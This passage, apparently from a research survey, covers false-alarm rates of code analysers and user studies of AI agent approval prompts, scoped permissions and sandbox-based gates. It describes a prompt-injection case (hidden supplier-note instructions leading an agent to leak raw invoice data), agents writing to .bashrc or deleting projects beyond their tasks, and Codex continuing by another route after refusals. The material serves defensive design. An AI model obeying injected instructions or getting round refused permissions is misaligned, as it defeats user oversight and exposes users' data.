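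Developers also leave real bugs unfixed when they consider them unimportant. In May 2009, hundreds of Google engineers spent a week reviewing warnings from FindBugs, a bug finder for Java. They filed bug reports for 44% of the 3,954 warnings they reviewed, but fixed only 16%. The precision figures for agent analysers rest mostly on researchers' own reading of the code, so they can be much higher than the share of reports that developers would act on.

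### The same warning at a different time

Facebook's experience with Infer, an analyser that looks for crashes and similar errors, shows that developers' response to warnings depends heavily on when they see them. The company first ran Infer every night over its whole Android app. The Infer team picked 20 to 30 results and assigned them to the developers who seemed best placed to fix them. Developers acted on almost none, although the team believed that fewer than 20% of the reports were wrong. Facebook then ran the same analysis on each proposed change and posted the results as comments in code review. Developers fixed over 70% of the problems reported this way.

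The developers described two problems with nightly reports. A nightly report interrupts someone working on something else, who has to recall how the old code works before judging the report. It may also reach the wrong person, since whoever wrote the code may have left. A comment on a change reaches the person who made the change while they still remember the code.

Timing may not explain the whole jump, because the two runs also reported different bugs. The nightly run covered old code that mostly worked, while the review comments covered only problems the change had introduced. Google found a similar difference when it surveyed its developers. They considered 74% of the problems flagged by the compiler to be real, but only 21% of those found in code that had already been merged. Sadowski and colleagues explain that testing and review have usually caught the serious errors by then.

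Showing warnings during code review does not help if developers distrust the tool. Google tried FindBugs three times between 2006 and 2011. The first attempt put the results on a separate web page, which developers rarely opened. In the second, a team sorted the warnings by hand and filed bug reports, which took too much work. The third posted warnings as code review comments, but developers lost confidence in the tool because of effective false positives. Each developer could also change the settings, so colleagues saw different results for the same code.

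Its successor, Tricorder, also posts its results in code review, and each comment has a "Please fix" and a "Not useful" button. If the "Not useful" clicks on an analyser exceed 10% of its "Please fix" clicks, Google switches it off until its authors improve it. In January 2018 reviewers clicked "Please fix" more than 5,000 times a day and "Not useful" about 250 times a day. These counts leave out warnings that people ignored.

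Google sets a stricter standard for checks that stop a program from compiling and allows them no effective false positives. Before switching on such a check, the responsible team fixes every existing case in the company's code.

### Why companies chose to miss bugs

Coverity deliberately made its analyser unsound. The tool ignored kinds of code that led to many false reports or made the analysis too complex, and in extreme cases it skipped whole files. The aim was to find as many real bugs as possible, not to prove that none remained. Suppose a sound tool finds all 50 bugs in a program but produces so many false reports that developers read none of its output. An unsound tool that finds 20 of the bugs is more useful if developers fix 14 of them.

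Commercial pressure also mostly favoured reducing false reports over catching more bugs, because customers saw every false report but seldom learned about a bug that the tool had missed. They learned about missed bugs mainly during sales trials, when some customers planted bugs or checked whether the tool found one that had recently caused them problems.

Google kept its widely used analysers simple because an analysis that follows data through the whole program would have needed a large investment to cover two billion lines of code, and more work to reduce its false positives. Google's teams also still had plenty of simple checks left to write.

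Facebook's engineers used advanced analysis and stressed that missed bugs mattered to them, but they gave up soundness where it stood in the way. One project set out to prove that Java programs were free of data races, in which two threads use the same memory at once and at least one of them writes to it. Then a team converting part of the Android app to run on several threads needed help within months, so the researchers dropped the goal of a proof and built a tool that found likely races quickly. They later proved that, under certain assumptions, an idealised version of the tool reports only real races, which is completeness rather than soundness. Developers fixed more than 2,500 of the tool's reports in the year to March 2018. In that time Facebook learned of only three Android races that the tool had missed, all because of errors in the tool's code.

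The number of false positives Facebook accepted depended on the kind of bug and on who read the report. It accepted more for security flaws. Its security analyser, Zoncolan, posted only its most reliable kinds of warning directly on a developer's change. Less certain warnings went to a security engineer on duty, and the rest went into a list for later security reviews. People acted on about 80% of Zoncolan's reports.

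Developers' wishes aren't enough to decide how unsound a tool should be. Many analysers ignore exceptions, the jumps a program makes when an error occurs, because following them all makes the analysis slower and less precise. In the Microsoft survey, developers ranked exceptions first among the gaps that tools should close. However, Christakis and Bird found no sign that the developers who asked for this would accept many more false positives.

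### Astrée

Engineers of safety-critical software cannot accept an analyser that misses errors in order to raise fewer false alarms, because one missed error may bring down an aircraft. They have shown that a sound analysis can raise few or no false alarms if it covers only a restricted class of programs.

Astrée is a sound analyser for C programs that use neither recursion nor dynamic memory allocation (requests for new memory while the program runs). It looks for run-time errors such as division by zero, arithmetic overflow and reading outside an array. In November 2003 it analysed the Airbus A340's primary flight control software, 132,000 lines of code, in 80 minutes on an ordinary PC. It raised no false alarms and proved that the software had no such errors, according to *The Astrée Static Analyzer*, a description by École Normale Supérieure, which developed the tool.

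Even a low rate of false alarms would have been a problem here. École Normale Supérieure points out that an analyser with one false alarm per 100 operations would raise 1,000 on a program with 100,000 operations. Engineers who lack the time to examine every alarm, as often happened with earlier tools, can fix only the definite errors and end up without a proof.

Astrée reaches its precision by keeping facts that a general analyser would lose. One example from the project is, slightly shortened:

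```
B = (X == 0);
if (!B) { Y = 1 / X; }
```

An analyser that describes `B` and `X` separately has to report a possible division by zero. Astrée records that `X` cannot be zero when `B` is false, so it reports nothing. The five-node workflow produced a false alarm because its graph had similarly lost the connection between the two branches that depended on `home`. Astrée also has special descriptions for digital filters, which are common in control software.

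Blanchet, Cousot and colleagues (2003), in *A Static Analyzer for Large Safety-Critical Software*, first refined a general analyser for one family of programs and then let users adapt it to each program through its settings. The first run on a new program usually leaves a few false alarms, which engineers remove by adjusting the analysis. The analyser proves only the absence of run-time errors. Cousot, Cousot and colleagues (2005) acknowledge that this is only part of verifying such software, since a program can run without these errors and still steer an aircraft wrongly.

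### How far this applies to agent harnesses

Reports about agent code mostly go to developers who can ignore them, as in these studies, so the limits of 10% to 30% are a reasonable first guide to which agent analysers developers would keep using. Of the analysers whose precision researchers measured on real projects, only IAL-Scan, with about 8% wrong reports, would meet Google's limit for code review, and only if developers acted on every report that the researchers considered correct. APSIS would meet it if bugs were as common as in its benchmark, but probably not on ordinary code. AgentFlow, with 27% wrong reports, would be just under the level at which Coverity's customers lost trust. With ClawAudit, where 88% were wrong, the first three reports would all be wrong about two-thirds of the time. Such unreliable reports might still be useful to security specialists, as Zoncolan's less reliable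 warnings were.

Google's rule for compiler errors is the closest match for a permission gate, because both stop the person or agent from continuing. By that standard, a gate should block only when its check is almost never wrong, and less certain findings should appear as warnings, as Althoubi proposed for shell commands.

The studies do not cover coding agents that read the warnings themselves. The limits of people's tolerance for false alarms may not apply to an agent, which can read every report and has no other work to return to. However, an agent that trusts wrong reports may change correct code to make a warning disappear. Johnson and colleagues' finding about unclear messages may carry over better, since an agent also needs to know what is wrong before it can fix it.

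Astrée's approach suits some parts of a harness more than others. A permission gate written in a small language such as Cedar is even simpler than flight control software, but an agent project that attaches tools while it runs has the kind of flexibility that Astrée rules out. École Normale Supérieure notes that false alarms can arise when the analysis leaves out facts about a program's environment. An engineer can state the range of values that a sensor may deliver, but only a check in the harness's own code can set such limits on a language model's output.

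## How users respond to approval prompts

A developer can ignore an analyser's warning and keep working, but an approval prompt usually blocks the agent until someone answers it. The quickest way to unblock it is to click "allow" without reading the prompt. Most research on how often people do this dates from 2026, and much of it relies on small groups, simulated tasks or self-reports.

### How an undecided check becomes a prompt

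Designers usually make a gate ask about the calls it can't decide, because denying them all would block a lot of harmless work.

Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, built a gate of this kind. A language model reads each tool's name, description and list of arguments and sorts the tool into categories such as spending, sending or deleting. The gate then applies the user's rule for that category. It asks the user if no rule exists, if the model's answer is invalid or if the model's confidence is low.

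Yan measured the tradeoff in asking for approval by simulating a rule that forbids one category of tools at a time. The gate failed to stop 14% of the tools in the forbidden category and wrongly stopped 4% of the others. When it asked about low-confidence cases, the share of forbidden tools that could run without review fell to 11%, but needless interruptions rose to 7%.

Approval prompts tend to appear when the gate lacks information about a call, and they often show the user only what the gate already had. For example, if an agent tries to run `python3 setup.py`, the gate can't determine what the script will do, and the user sees the same command. Approving it permits whatever the script contains. The user could read the script first, but that takes much longer than clicking and would usually reveal no problem.

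Most prompts are also about harmless calls. In the earlier hypothetical run of 1,000 writes with 10 violations, a gate that asked instead of blocking would show 108 prompts, 99 of them about harmless writes. A user who approved every prompt unread would be right 11 times out of 12. The likely result is what security researchers call approval fatigue, in which people stop examining requests because there are so many, and approve them by habit or switch the prompts off.

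### Reports of damaged files

Zhong, Liao and colleagues (2026), in *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*, collected 290 public reports of agents that misused their access to files between February 2024 and March 2026. They found 205 on GitHub and the rest on social media, product forums, blogs and a public database of security flaws. Confirmed harm is described in 158 of the reports, while 49 demonstrate an attack and 83 describe a weakness without demonstrated harm.

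The researchers attributed each report to the model, the harness or the user's review of the agent's actions, and often to more than one. User review contributed to 105 reports. In 80, the action was approved automatically, for example in what users call "YOLO mode", which allows everything without asking. In 31, the prompt did not give the user enough information to judge the action. At least six reports fall into both groups.

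Needless blocks also led some users to switch off their own protection. One user of Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, disabled its protection against deletion so that the agent could clean up duplicate files. Blocking that cleanup was a false alarm by the user's standard, but with the protection off, the agent later deleted 90% of the project.

These counts show that automatic approval is common in reported accidents, but not how much it raises the risk. People post about lost files but rarely about uneventful sessions, and nobody knows how many sessions ran with automatic approval. The reports also don't show how many of the 80 actions a user would have refused if prompted. The labels come partly from an AI agent, which first classified 190 reports before the researchers reviewed its work.

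### What developers say about their own habits

Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, interviewed 18 software practitioners who use agents and then surveyed 115, of whom 107 answered the questions about permissions. Respondents could choose several answers:

| Reported habit | Share of 107 respondents |
|---|---|
| Read requests carefully | 47.7% |
| Skim requests | 33.6% |
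| Check the file that the request names | 31.8% |
| Focus on the command or title | 25.2% |
| Approve by default | 20.6% |
| Have become less careful over time | 33.6% |

The interviewees gave practical reasons. One said there were too many requests to go through. Another said having to click every ten seconds defeated the purpose of working faster, and a third often approved requests without much thought when rushing to deliver something.

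Users' attention also depends on the request. In the survey, 76.6% said they check requests to write, delete or gain higher privileges more carefully, and 63.6% said they look more closely at unexpected requests. Someone who skims a request to read a file may therefore still check a deletion carefully, if the prompt shows that the call deletes something. But a script that deletes files can look like an ordinary test run.

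Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), in *From Delegation to Action Approval*, asked 203 developers how often they approve seven types of agent action without close review. For at least one type, 64% said they often do so. For individual types, the share ranged from 21% for reading passwords and other sensitive files to 36% for using the internet or connected tools.

Developers who review an agent's code carefully aren't necessarily careful about approving its actions. Of the 105 respondents who carefully review most or all of the code an agent writes, 61% often approve at least one type of action without close review, compared with 67% of the other respondents, a difference well within the range of chance. Reviewing the code can't make up for careless approvals, because a command can delete data or expose a password without changing the code. Developers who inspect the exact lines an agent changed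 did report more care with four of the seven types of action.

Among developers who knew of at least one security or privacy problem involving agents, 70% often approved something without close review, compared with 43% of those who knew of none. The gap remained after the researchers adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents. Heavy users probably hear about more incidents and also approve more requests, and the adjustment may have removed only part of that effect. Learning about incidents is unlikely to make people careless.

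Both surveys depend on volunteers describing themselves, and people may not notice or admit how little they read. Answers also varied with the question. In the survey by Salerno and colleagues, 70.1% reported paying close attention to permissions, but only 47.7% reported reading requests carefully. The developers' survey also received many poor-quality responses. It kept only 203 of 583 submissions and dropped 251 because respondents finished implausibly fast.

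### Usage data from Claude Code

Claude Code users approve 93% of permission prompts, according to an Anthropic figure that Salerno and colleagues cite. The figure describes what people did, so it avoids the weakness of the surveys. But it could come from attentive users whose prompts are mostly harmless, or from inattentive users who occasionally refuse something. In the hypothetical run with 108 prompts, a user who judged every request correctly would approve 99 of them, or about 92%, and someone who read nothing would approve all of them. To tell which kind of user the 93% reflects, we would need to know how many of the approved calls the users would have refused after a close look.

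Anthropic also analysed records from millions of Claude Code sessions. According to Wu and colleagues' summary, experienced users switch on automatic approval more often but also interrupt the agent more often. They may be supervising the work as a whole instead of deciding on each call. This is a reasonable way to notice an agent going in the wrong direction, but it works less well for a single harmful call, since an email or a deletion can take effect before anyone intervenes.

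### Approvals with a limited scope

The choices that a prompt offers may be part of the problem. For tools connected through the Model Context Protocol, many harnesses offer only "Allow Once", "Always Allow" and a refusal. *Options, Not Clicks* (Li, Khabra and colleagues, 2026) gives an example close to the `write_file` case. An agent fixes a bug and writes a unit test inside the project, as the user asked, and then reads a secret key and writes to `.bashrc`. If the user had chosen "Always Allow" for the writing tool at the first write, the write to `.bashrc` would go through without a prompt.

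Their system, ConLeash, sits between the harness and the tools and gives each call a description with four parts:

φ = ⟨l_i, l_o, τ, E⟩

Here l_i is the range of resources that the call reads from or acts on, l_o is where its output goes, τ is how sensitive the data is, and E is the set of effects, such as reading or writing. Each part has an order from narrow to broad. A new call φ runs without a prompt if an earlier approval φ′ is at least as broad in every part, which the researchers write as

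φ ⊑ φ′

If no approval covers the call, ConLeash prompts the user and offers approvals of different scope. For a call on `/project/src/lib/utils.py`, the user might approve that file, everything in `lib` or everything under `src`. The approval for the unit test would not cover `.bashrc`, so the user would get a new prompt. Users can also state prohibitions in ordinary language, such as never sending files from outside the project to third parties, and no approval overrides them.

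A language model works out the four parts, and ordinary code compares them. On 984 test sequences, which the researchers generated with a language model and checked by hand, ConLeash let 98.3% of harmless calls through without a prompt and caught 99.4% of the calls that needed a prompt or a block. Some needless prompts occurred because the model described a later call more strictly than an earlier call to the same tool.

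Li and colleagues then tested the prompts on 16 people, paying each $25 for a session of about an hour. In a questionnaire beforehand, 13 said they use "Always Allow" just to get rid of prompts, and only 3 said they read prompts carefully. Each participant then completed three tasks with ConLeash and three with ordinary prompts. In four of the six tasks, the agent went beyond what the user had asked for.

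With ConLeash, participants chose a lasting approval in 46.3% of their decisions, compared with 13.3% with ordinary prompts. Earlier approvals covered 41.9% of tool calls, so participants got no prompt for those. Fifteen participants preferred ConLeash and one had no preference.

The figure of 13 out of 16 is weaker evidence than it looks. The question allowed the answers "never", "sometimes", "often" and "always", so the 13 may include people who only sometimes dismiss prompts this way. The 16 were not a random sample of users, and even if they were, the true share could lie anywhere between about 54% and 96%. During the experiment, the same people chose a blanket approval in only 13.3% of their decisions, though they may have been more careful than usual because a researcher was watching over a video call.

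The experiment gives good evidence that people like scoped approvals and use them. It is less certain that these approvals protect users better, because the reported results compare people's choices and ratings but don't count the harmful calls they let through. Li and colleagues argue that protection improves because every call outside an approved scope triggers a new prompt. That prompt helps only if the user reads it, and a user who wants to avoid prompts can pick the widest scope available.

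### Four ways to show the same request

An approval prompt can be hard to judge even for a user who reads it. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who asks an agent to reconcile supplier invoices and send only the summary totals to an auditor. Instructions hidden in a supplier's note lead the agent to copy the raw invoice rows into `report.csv`, and the agent then asks for permission to send `report.csv` to the auditor. The tool, the recipient and the file name all look right. The user can spot the problem only by connecting the file to the earlier step that created it.

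Eighty unpaid volunteers recruited through social media were assigned to four displays, with 20 people per display. Each person judged 12 requests, half of them harmful, for a total of 960 decisions.

| Display | What the reviewer sees | Harmful requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Conventional prompt | A short description of the action | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
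| Exact action | The description and the tool's actual arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Chronological log | Also the user's original instructions and every earlier step | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| Consequence view | The same facts as the log, with a sentence on their combined effect | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

In the invoice example, the consequence view shows that the attachment was built from raw invoice rows and that the agent is about to send it to the auditor. The reviewer then decides whether this breaks the instructions.

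Most of the improvement came from showing more information. Harmful approvals were 22.5 percentage points lower with the log than with the conventional prompt, and another 8.3 points lower with the consequence view. After adjustment for differences between tasks and participants, the second drop was an estimated 7.9 points, with a 95% interval from a fall of 19.7 to a rise of 3.8. The consequence view may therefore be no better than the log at preventing harmful approvals. When a violation depended on a chain of several steps, reviewers approved 7 of 30 harmful requests with each of these two displays.

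The consequence view also led reviewers to raise more false alarms. They refused 14.2% of harmless requests with it, compared with 8.3% with the conventional prompt. Each decision took twice as long. At the median times, 100 prompts a day would take about 55 minutes with the consequence view and 27 minutes with the conventional prompt. Users who already find prompts tiring might turn off the longer ones.

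The volunteers judged invented requests for about 20 minutes, and half of the requests were harmful. People who use an agent every day see far fewer harmful requests and would probably be less alert, so they may approve a larger share of them. The ranking of the displays is more likely than the approval rates to hold in daily use, although it could change after weeks if people learn to skip the extra text.

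### Rules that users write in advance

A user could avoid many prompts by answering questions in advance. Yan tested this with 113 people from outside the software industry, who watched a simulated assistant carry out 18 actions in a day of email, travel and errands. The user's instructions required 11 of the actions. The other seven, such as buying a $25 airport lounge pass or reading private messages, went beyond the instructions.

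One group approved or denied every action. A second group got prompts only for actions that a language model had flagged. A third group first set a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories: spending money, sending or publishing, deleting, and reading private information.

| | Every action needs approval | Model flags actions | Users write rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Participants | 34 | 44 | 35 |
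| Average number of prompts | 18.0 | 10.0 | 10.9 |
| Prompts about unrequested actions that users approved | 40.3% | 46.1% | 66.8% |
| Unrequested actions blocked | 59.6% | 53.9% | 39.6% |
| Average time spent, including writing rules | 142 s | 120 s | 129 s |

The people who wrote rules got the weakest protection. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, "never" for 16 and "allow" for 10, so they still had to make most decisions while the agent was running. In this group, 148 unrequested actions went ahead, 133 because the user approved a prompt and 15 because of an "allow" rule.

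The approval rate is high partly because people who wrote "never" for a category got no prompts about it, so the prompts went to those who were more willing to say yes. But this explains only part of the difference. Even counting the automatic blocks, 60.4% of the unrequested actions went ahead in the group that wrote rules, compared with 40.3% in the group asked to approve every action. Users may feel that an action has already passed a check when their own rule triggers the prompt, but the experiment did not test this.

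Yan recruited some participants for the rule-writing group after random assignment had ended, so the groups may differ in other ways. The difference from the group with the model is also not statistically reliable after correction for multiple comparisons. An approval was not always a lapse of attention. Nearly everyone allowed the assistant to call the airport and confirm the flight, which the instructions had not asked for but a traveller might welcome. Without that action, the approval rates are 32%, 40% and 61%, so the order of the groups stays the same. Someone who wants the lounge pass may also approve it knowingly, especially when the money isn't real. For that person the prompt would be a false alarm, even though it was correct given the assigned task.

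### Predicting the user's answer

Other researchers want software to learn from users' past answers and answer later prompts for them. In *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, Wu, Yang and colleagues (2025) studied 203 people recruited through Prolific, after excluding two others for invalid responses. The participants imagined training a personal assistant and decided which of their data it could share with various tools. A quarter of the 20 permission questions included data that the task did not need.

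Participants' choices were fairly consistent within an area of life such as entertainment, and often resembled those of other participants. A model that combined both sources of information predicted 85.1% of the choices correctly, and 94.4% of those it was most confident about. Without a user's earlier choices, its accuracy was 66.9%. Adding the user's answers to one to four earlier requests raised accuracy by 10.8 percentage points.

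These figures measure agreement with what users chose, and users often chose badly. Almost all participants (97.0%) shared more than the task required at least once. They shared about 78% of the unnecessary items they wrongly believed were necessary, and about 38% of those they correctly recognised as unnecessary. A predictor that copied these decisions perfectly would also share too much, without a prompt that might make the user reconsider.

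The questions were also hypothetical, and the participants' only task was to answer them carefully. Real approval records would include hurried answers, so the same method might reveal less about what people want.

### Trust or fatigue

The prediction study treats users' past answers as preferences worth learning, but Salerno and colleagues warn against this because their interviewees described approving requests out of habit, tiredness or time pressure. Trust may also explain repeated approval. In their survey, 57.0% of respondents said they were more likely to grant a permission when they trusted the tool or its vendor, and 31.8% said they supervised an agent less closely after it had worked reliably.

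In ordinary use, the two explanations predict much the same behaviour. Every harmless prompt adds to a user's workload and gives the user another reason to trust the agent, so approvals become quicker either way. Researchers could tell the explanations apart by planting an obviously harmful request after different amounts of use. A user who trusts the agent but still reads the prompts should refuse the request, while a user who has stopped reading would approve it. None of these studies ran such a test over weeks of real work.

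Yan's experiment gives some evidence against the simplest fatigue explanation, that people approve more because they have seen more prompts. The two groups that saw 10 or 11 prompts approved a larger share of the unrequested actions than the group that saw 18. However, participants spent only about two minutes on their decisions, too short a time for long-term habits to form. The result mainly gives reason to doubt that showing fewer prompts will by itself make people read the remaining ones more carefully.

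The harness should remember a user's answer if repeated approvals express a settled preference, because asking again is a needless interruption. But if the approvals come from fatigue, remembering the answer makes a careless click permanent. ConLeash asks users to choose the scope of a lasting approval instead of guessing it, though a tired user can make that choice carelessly too.

### When users approve what a sound gate flags

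If a gate asks about every call that breaks the rule, its designer can prove that no such call runs without a person's approval. How much harm this prevents depends on the person. Let r be the share of rule-breaking calls that the gate asks about, and let a be the share of those calls that users approve. Together, the gate and the user stop

r · (1 − a)

of the rule-breaking calls. For a sound gate, r = 1. With the 55.0% of harmful requests that reviewers approved when they saw a conventional prompt, a sound gate would stop only 45% of violations. A gate that missed 10% of violations but used the consequence view, where reviewers approved 24.2%, would stop about 68%. The calculation borrows its approval rates from the volunteers in the display experiment, so the exact figures would differ elsewhere.

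The group that had the model in Yan's study comes close to a direct test of whether accurate flags protect users. The model flagged all seven unrequested actions and only three of the 11 required ones. Its precision on these 18 actions was therefore 70%, which is better than the gate's in the hypothetical run of 1,000 writes. Users still approved 46.1% of the unrequested actions it flagged. Catching every unrequested action with few false alarms was not enough to protect them, although some of those approvals were probably deliberate.

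Where a check has enough information to decide, blocking may therefore protect better than asking. Hossain and colleagues also ran their monitor without human reviewers, and it detected 89.2% of 120 violations. When it blocked every call that it judged to be a violation or lacked the evidence to judge, the share of cases in which one agent carried out a harmful action fell from 43.3% to 5.0%, with a small loss in legitimate tasks. The volunteers judged different test cases, so the 5.0% is not directly comparable with the 24.2% that they approved.

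Refusing a request may not stop the agent from trying another way either. One practitioner whom Salerno and colleagues interviewed refused several requests from Codex, which then stopped asking and continued by another route. The practitioner couldn't tell whether the new route respected the limits that had led them to refuse. A refusal usually covers only one call. A sound gate would check the new route against the same rule, but if it couldn't decide that case either, it would prompt the user again.

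## Designs that reduce false alarms

A check can raise fewer false alarms if it gets more information, or if its designers accept that it will miss some violations. Adding information preserves soundness as long as the information is correct. Restricted policy languages, finer information-flow labels and ConLeash's scoped approvals all add information. So do the designs that follow, which get it from the program's code, its developers, the arguments of the actual call, or a language model.

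### Refining a check only where an alarm is false

Tracking the value of `home` would have prevented the false alarm in the five-node workflow, but tracking every variable can make a search far too large. Counterexample-guided abstraction refinement, which Edmund Clarke and colleagues introduced in 2000, adds a variable only when an alarm shows that it matters. The method repeats four steps:

1. Search the simplified model for a violation. If there is none, the program obeys the rule.
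2. Write down, as a formula, the conditions under which the program would follow the reported path.
3. Give the formula to a solver. If it has a solution, the path can happen and the alarm is real.
4. If it has no solution, add the fact that rules out the path to the model, and search again.

In the workflow, the search returns the path `start`, `save`, `write_home`. The step from `start` to `save` needs `home` to be false, and the step from `save` to `write_home` needs it to be true:

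¬home ∧ home

No value satisfies this, so the method adds `home` to the model. The search now keeps track of the node, the state of the rule's automaton and the value of `home`:

| `home` | What the search reaches |
|---|---|
| true | `start` (unreviewed), `review` (reviewed), `save` (reviewed), `write_home` (reviewed), `end` (reviewed) |
| false | `start` (unreviewed), `save` (unreviewed), `end` (unreviewed) |

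None of these eight combinations breaks the rule, so the alarm disappears. A full search of the original graph also visits at least eight pairs, so the extra variable did not make this search larger.

If the workflow prompted the model again after `save`, the two branches would depend on two separate answers:

¬home₁ ∧ home₂

This formula has a solution, so the method correctly reports a violation. The method stays sound because it removes only paths that the solver has proved impossible.

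Rice's theorem implies that refinement cannot always succeed. Suppose a loop increases two counters together, and an alarm is real only if they can differ. Refinement may rule out the pair (1, 2), then (2, 3), and so on, without ever finding that the counters are always equal. The tool then has to stop at a time limit and keep the alarm. Refinement doesn't help with `write_file` either, because the solver will always find a file path outside the workspace.

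### Annotations from developers

Suppose `write_file` calls a helper function, `check_path`, that stops with an error if a path leads outside the workspace. An analyser that examines one function at a time misses this check and reports the write, as ClawAudit's rules did in similar cases. The developer can attach an annotation to the helper, a statement for the analyser to use:

if `check_path(p)` returns normally, then inside(resolve(p), W)

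If a helper is annotated, the analyser can drop the report without reading the helper's code. This remains sound if the analyser also checks the code against the annotation, but if it trusts the annotation unchecked, a mistake there can hide a real violation.

Annotations can also describe what library functions do. Adam and colleagues propose annotating the common functions for writing files and contacting the network, since most tools use a few popular libraries. If a tool bypasses them and calls the operating system directly, the analyser should reject it or assume a very broad effect. A missing annotation then causes a false alarm rather than a missed violation.

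In the audit of AgentFlow, correct tool labels would have prevented 25 of the 27 false alarms and raised precision from 73% to 97%. Someone would have to write the labels and keep them current, because a tool labelled "read-only" that later gains a write function would go unreported.

### Brown University's hybrid design

Annotations can't tell an analyser which path the model will choose. Adam and colleagues, who work at Brown University, leave that question to a small sandbox inside the tool and use static analysis to prove that the tool can't bypass it. For `write_file`, the design works as follows:

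1. The analyser lists the tool's effects, including the hidden metrics line. Under the workspace rule, the harness has to reject the tool, because it could write anywhere.
2. The tool's developer replaces the ordinary write with one from a sandbox library and gives the tool an extra argument for the sandbox's settings. The harness fills in this argument, not the model.
3. The analyser runs again. It checks that risky operations go through a sandbox and that nothing in the tool can alter the settings before the sandbox uses them. It lists any operation without a sandbox, and the harness rejects the tool unless the policy explicitly allows that effect.
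4. When the model requests a call, the harness derives the limits for that call from the user's policy and sends them along. Just before the write, the sandbox compares the actual path with the limits, and it refuses `.bashrc`.

The analyser now has to prove only that every write passes through the sandbox. This doesn't depend on the path, so the unknown path no longer causes an alarm.

In this example, the metrics call still runs outside a sandbox. The researchers' sample policy allows network traffic unless the session contains sensitive data. The harness would therefore allow the tool in an open-source project and refuse it in a proprietary one, even if the user needs the file. That refusal is correct, since the call would reveal the size of private content to an outside service. The developer could avoid the refusal by sandboxing the metrics call too.

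The researchers tested a prototype on an existing tool server for code editors, written in Rust, to which they added the metrics line. They recorded three sessions with Claude models and replayed them under four kinds of protection. Each session had a harmless version and a version that broke the user's policy:

- The agent saves a key in the project's settings file, `.env`, and adds lines to `.bashrc`. In the harmful version, the model guesses the wrong folder for `.env`.
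- The agent edits proprietary code. In the harmful version, the tool also sends out metrics.
- The agent publishes a project on GitHub. In the harmful version, `.env` contains a secret key.

| Protection | Harmless versions allowed | Harmful versions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| None | 3 of 3 | 0 of 3 |
| One sandbox with a fixed policy | 2 of 3 | 1 of 3 |
| Static analysis alone | 2 of 3 | 3 of 3 |
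| Hybrid design | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 |

In the first session, the hybrid design adjusts its limits to the user's request, so the policy permits the write to `.bashrc` that the user asked for. In the GitHub session, the harness can hide `.env` from the publishing command and still publish the rest of the project.

Six cases show that the design can work, but they are far too few to estimate a false-alarm rate. The researchers also assumed a source that supplies the right policy for each request, so the test doesn't include needless blocks caused by a wrong policy. The guarantee depends on several other conditions:

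- The server must run the same program that the analyser examined. Proving this takes remote attestation, in which special hardware vouches for the running code. Adam and colleagues name it as something a full system would need.
- The sandbox library must be correct, because the analyser trusts it.
- The analyser must find every effect. Rust's strict rules make this easier, and the researchers expect more needless rejections for Python and JavaScript.
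- Nobody may have tampered with the server's machine or operating system.

Some false alarms remain even for Rust. The prototype controls network access by domain name, so it can't distinguish reading a social media post from publishing one and has to treat both as the riskier action. Blocking a call late in a task can also leave earlier steps half finished. The researchers suggest grouping calls so that either all of them take effect or none do.

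### EVIDENT

Refinement and annotations need someone to find the fact that clears an alarm. In Li, Zhou and colleagues (2026), *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Program Analysis, Part III*, a language model looks for that fact, but a sound analyser gives the verdict. Their system, EVIDENT, examines warnings about drivers in Android's kernel, the core of the operating system. Analysing a whole kernel precisely is impractical, but analysing one function by itself misses the checks that its callers made.

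The model therefore writes a small C program that creates the objects the function needs and calls it. (The researchers call this program a harness, but it is unrelated to an agent's harness.) Frama-C/Eva, an analyser based on abstract interpretation, then examines the program. EVIDENT drops the warning only if Eva proves the reported error can't occur in that program.

An earlier model-based filter and human reviewers both overlooked one of the real bugs, in a driver whose check looks sufficient. The driver rejects a user's number if it is greater than 16 and otherwise uses it as a limit for writing into an array of 16 items. But the number has 64 bits and can be negative, so −(2³² − 17) passes the check. The driver then converts it to 32 bits, which turns it into 17, and writes beyond the end of the array.

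A model that decided the case itself could easily accept the check as proof of safety. A model that writes the setup program could make the same mistake by limiting the input to between 0 and 16. Eva would then correctly prove that the wrong program is safe. EVIDENT guards against this with three tests:

- Every numeric input must cover the full range of its type when the driver code starts.
- Eva must reach the operation that the warning concerns.
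- Eva must not skip an intermediate point on the reported path and still reach a later one.

If a test fails, the model gets an error message and tries again. If it can't fix the program, EVIDENT keeps the warning.

The researchers used 200 warnings from two existing detectors, 40 of them confirmed bugs and 160 false alarms. With four different language models, EVIDENT removed between 48.8% and 63.8% of the false alarms and lost no confirmed bug. With GPT-5.5, they also compared it with BugLens, an earlier system in which the model decides, and with the coding agent Codex:

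| Method, all with GPT-5.5 | False alarms removed | Confirmed bugs lost | Warnings left to read | Share of those that are bugs |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| EVIDENT | 102 of 160 | 0 of 40 | 98 | 41% |
| BugLens | 127 of 160 | 14 of 40 | 59 | 44% |
| Codex | 124 of 160 | 18 of 40 | 58 | 38% |
| Codex, told to avoid losing bugs | 123 of 160 | 11 of 40 | 66 | 44% |

The remaining lists have nearly the same precision, so a developer who judged the methods by their false alarms would see little difference. The model-decided lists are shorter, but they omit between a quarter and nearly half of the bugs.

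The two roles differ in what other software can check. To confirm a bug, a model needs to find one run that triggers it, but to dismiss a warning it has to rule out every run, which a written explanation can't establish. Software can test the assumptions in a program, however, and EVIDENT can reject a program that restricts an input. When Li and colleagues let GPT-5.5 choose the input ranges without these tests, the system lost nine bugs. When they gave GPT-5.5 Eva's finished results and let it make the final decision, the system lost four bugs and removed four fewer false alarms than Eva had. In three of those four cases, GPT-5.5 had reasoned wrongly about C's integers.

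EVIDENT still isn't sound, because the three tests don't prove that the setup program includes every run that matters. It lost none of the 40 bugs, but its true loss rate could still be as high as about 7%. Also, 39 of the 40 bugs came from one detector, and the researchers developed the tests on the same 200 warnings, although with a different language model.

None of the code analysed with EVIDENT came from an agent. Kernel drivers, however, share a difficulty with agent frameworks, since the kernel calls driver functions through stored pointers, much as a framework looks up a tool by name. The setup program in EVIDENT's model restores those connections. But EVIDENT needs a precise, sound analyser for the language being checked, and such analysis is much harder for the Python and JavaScript that many tool servers use.

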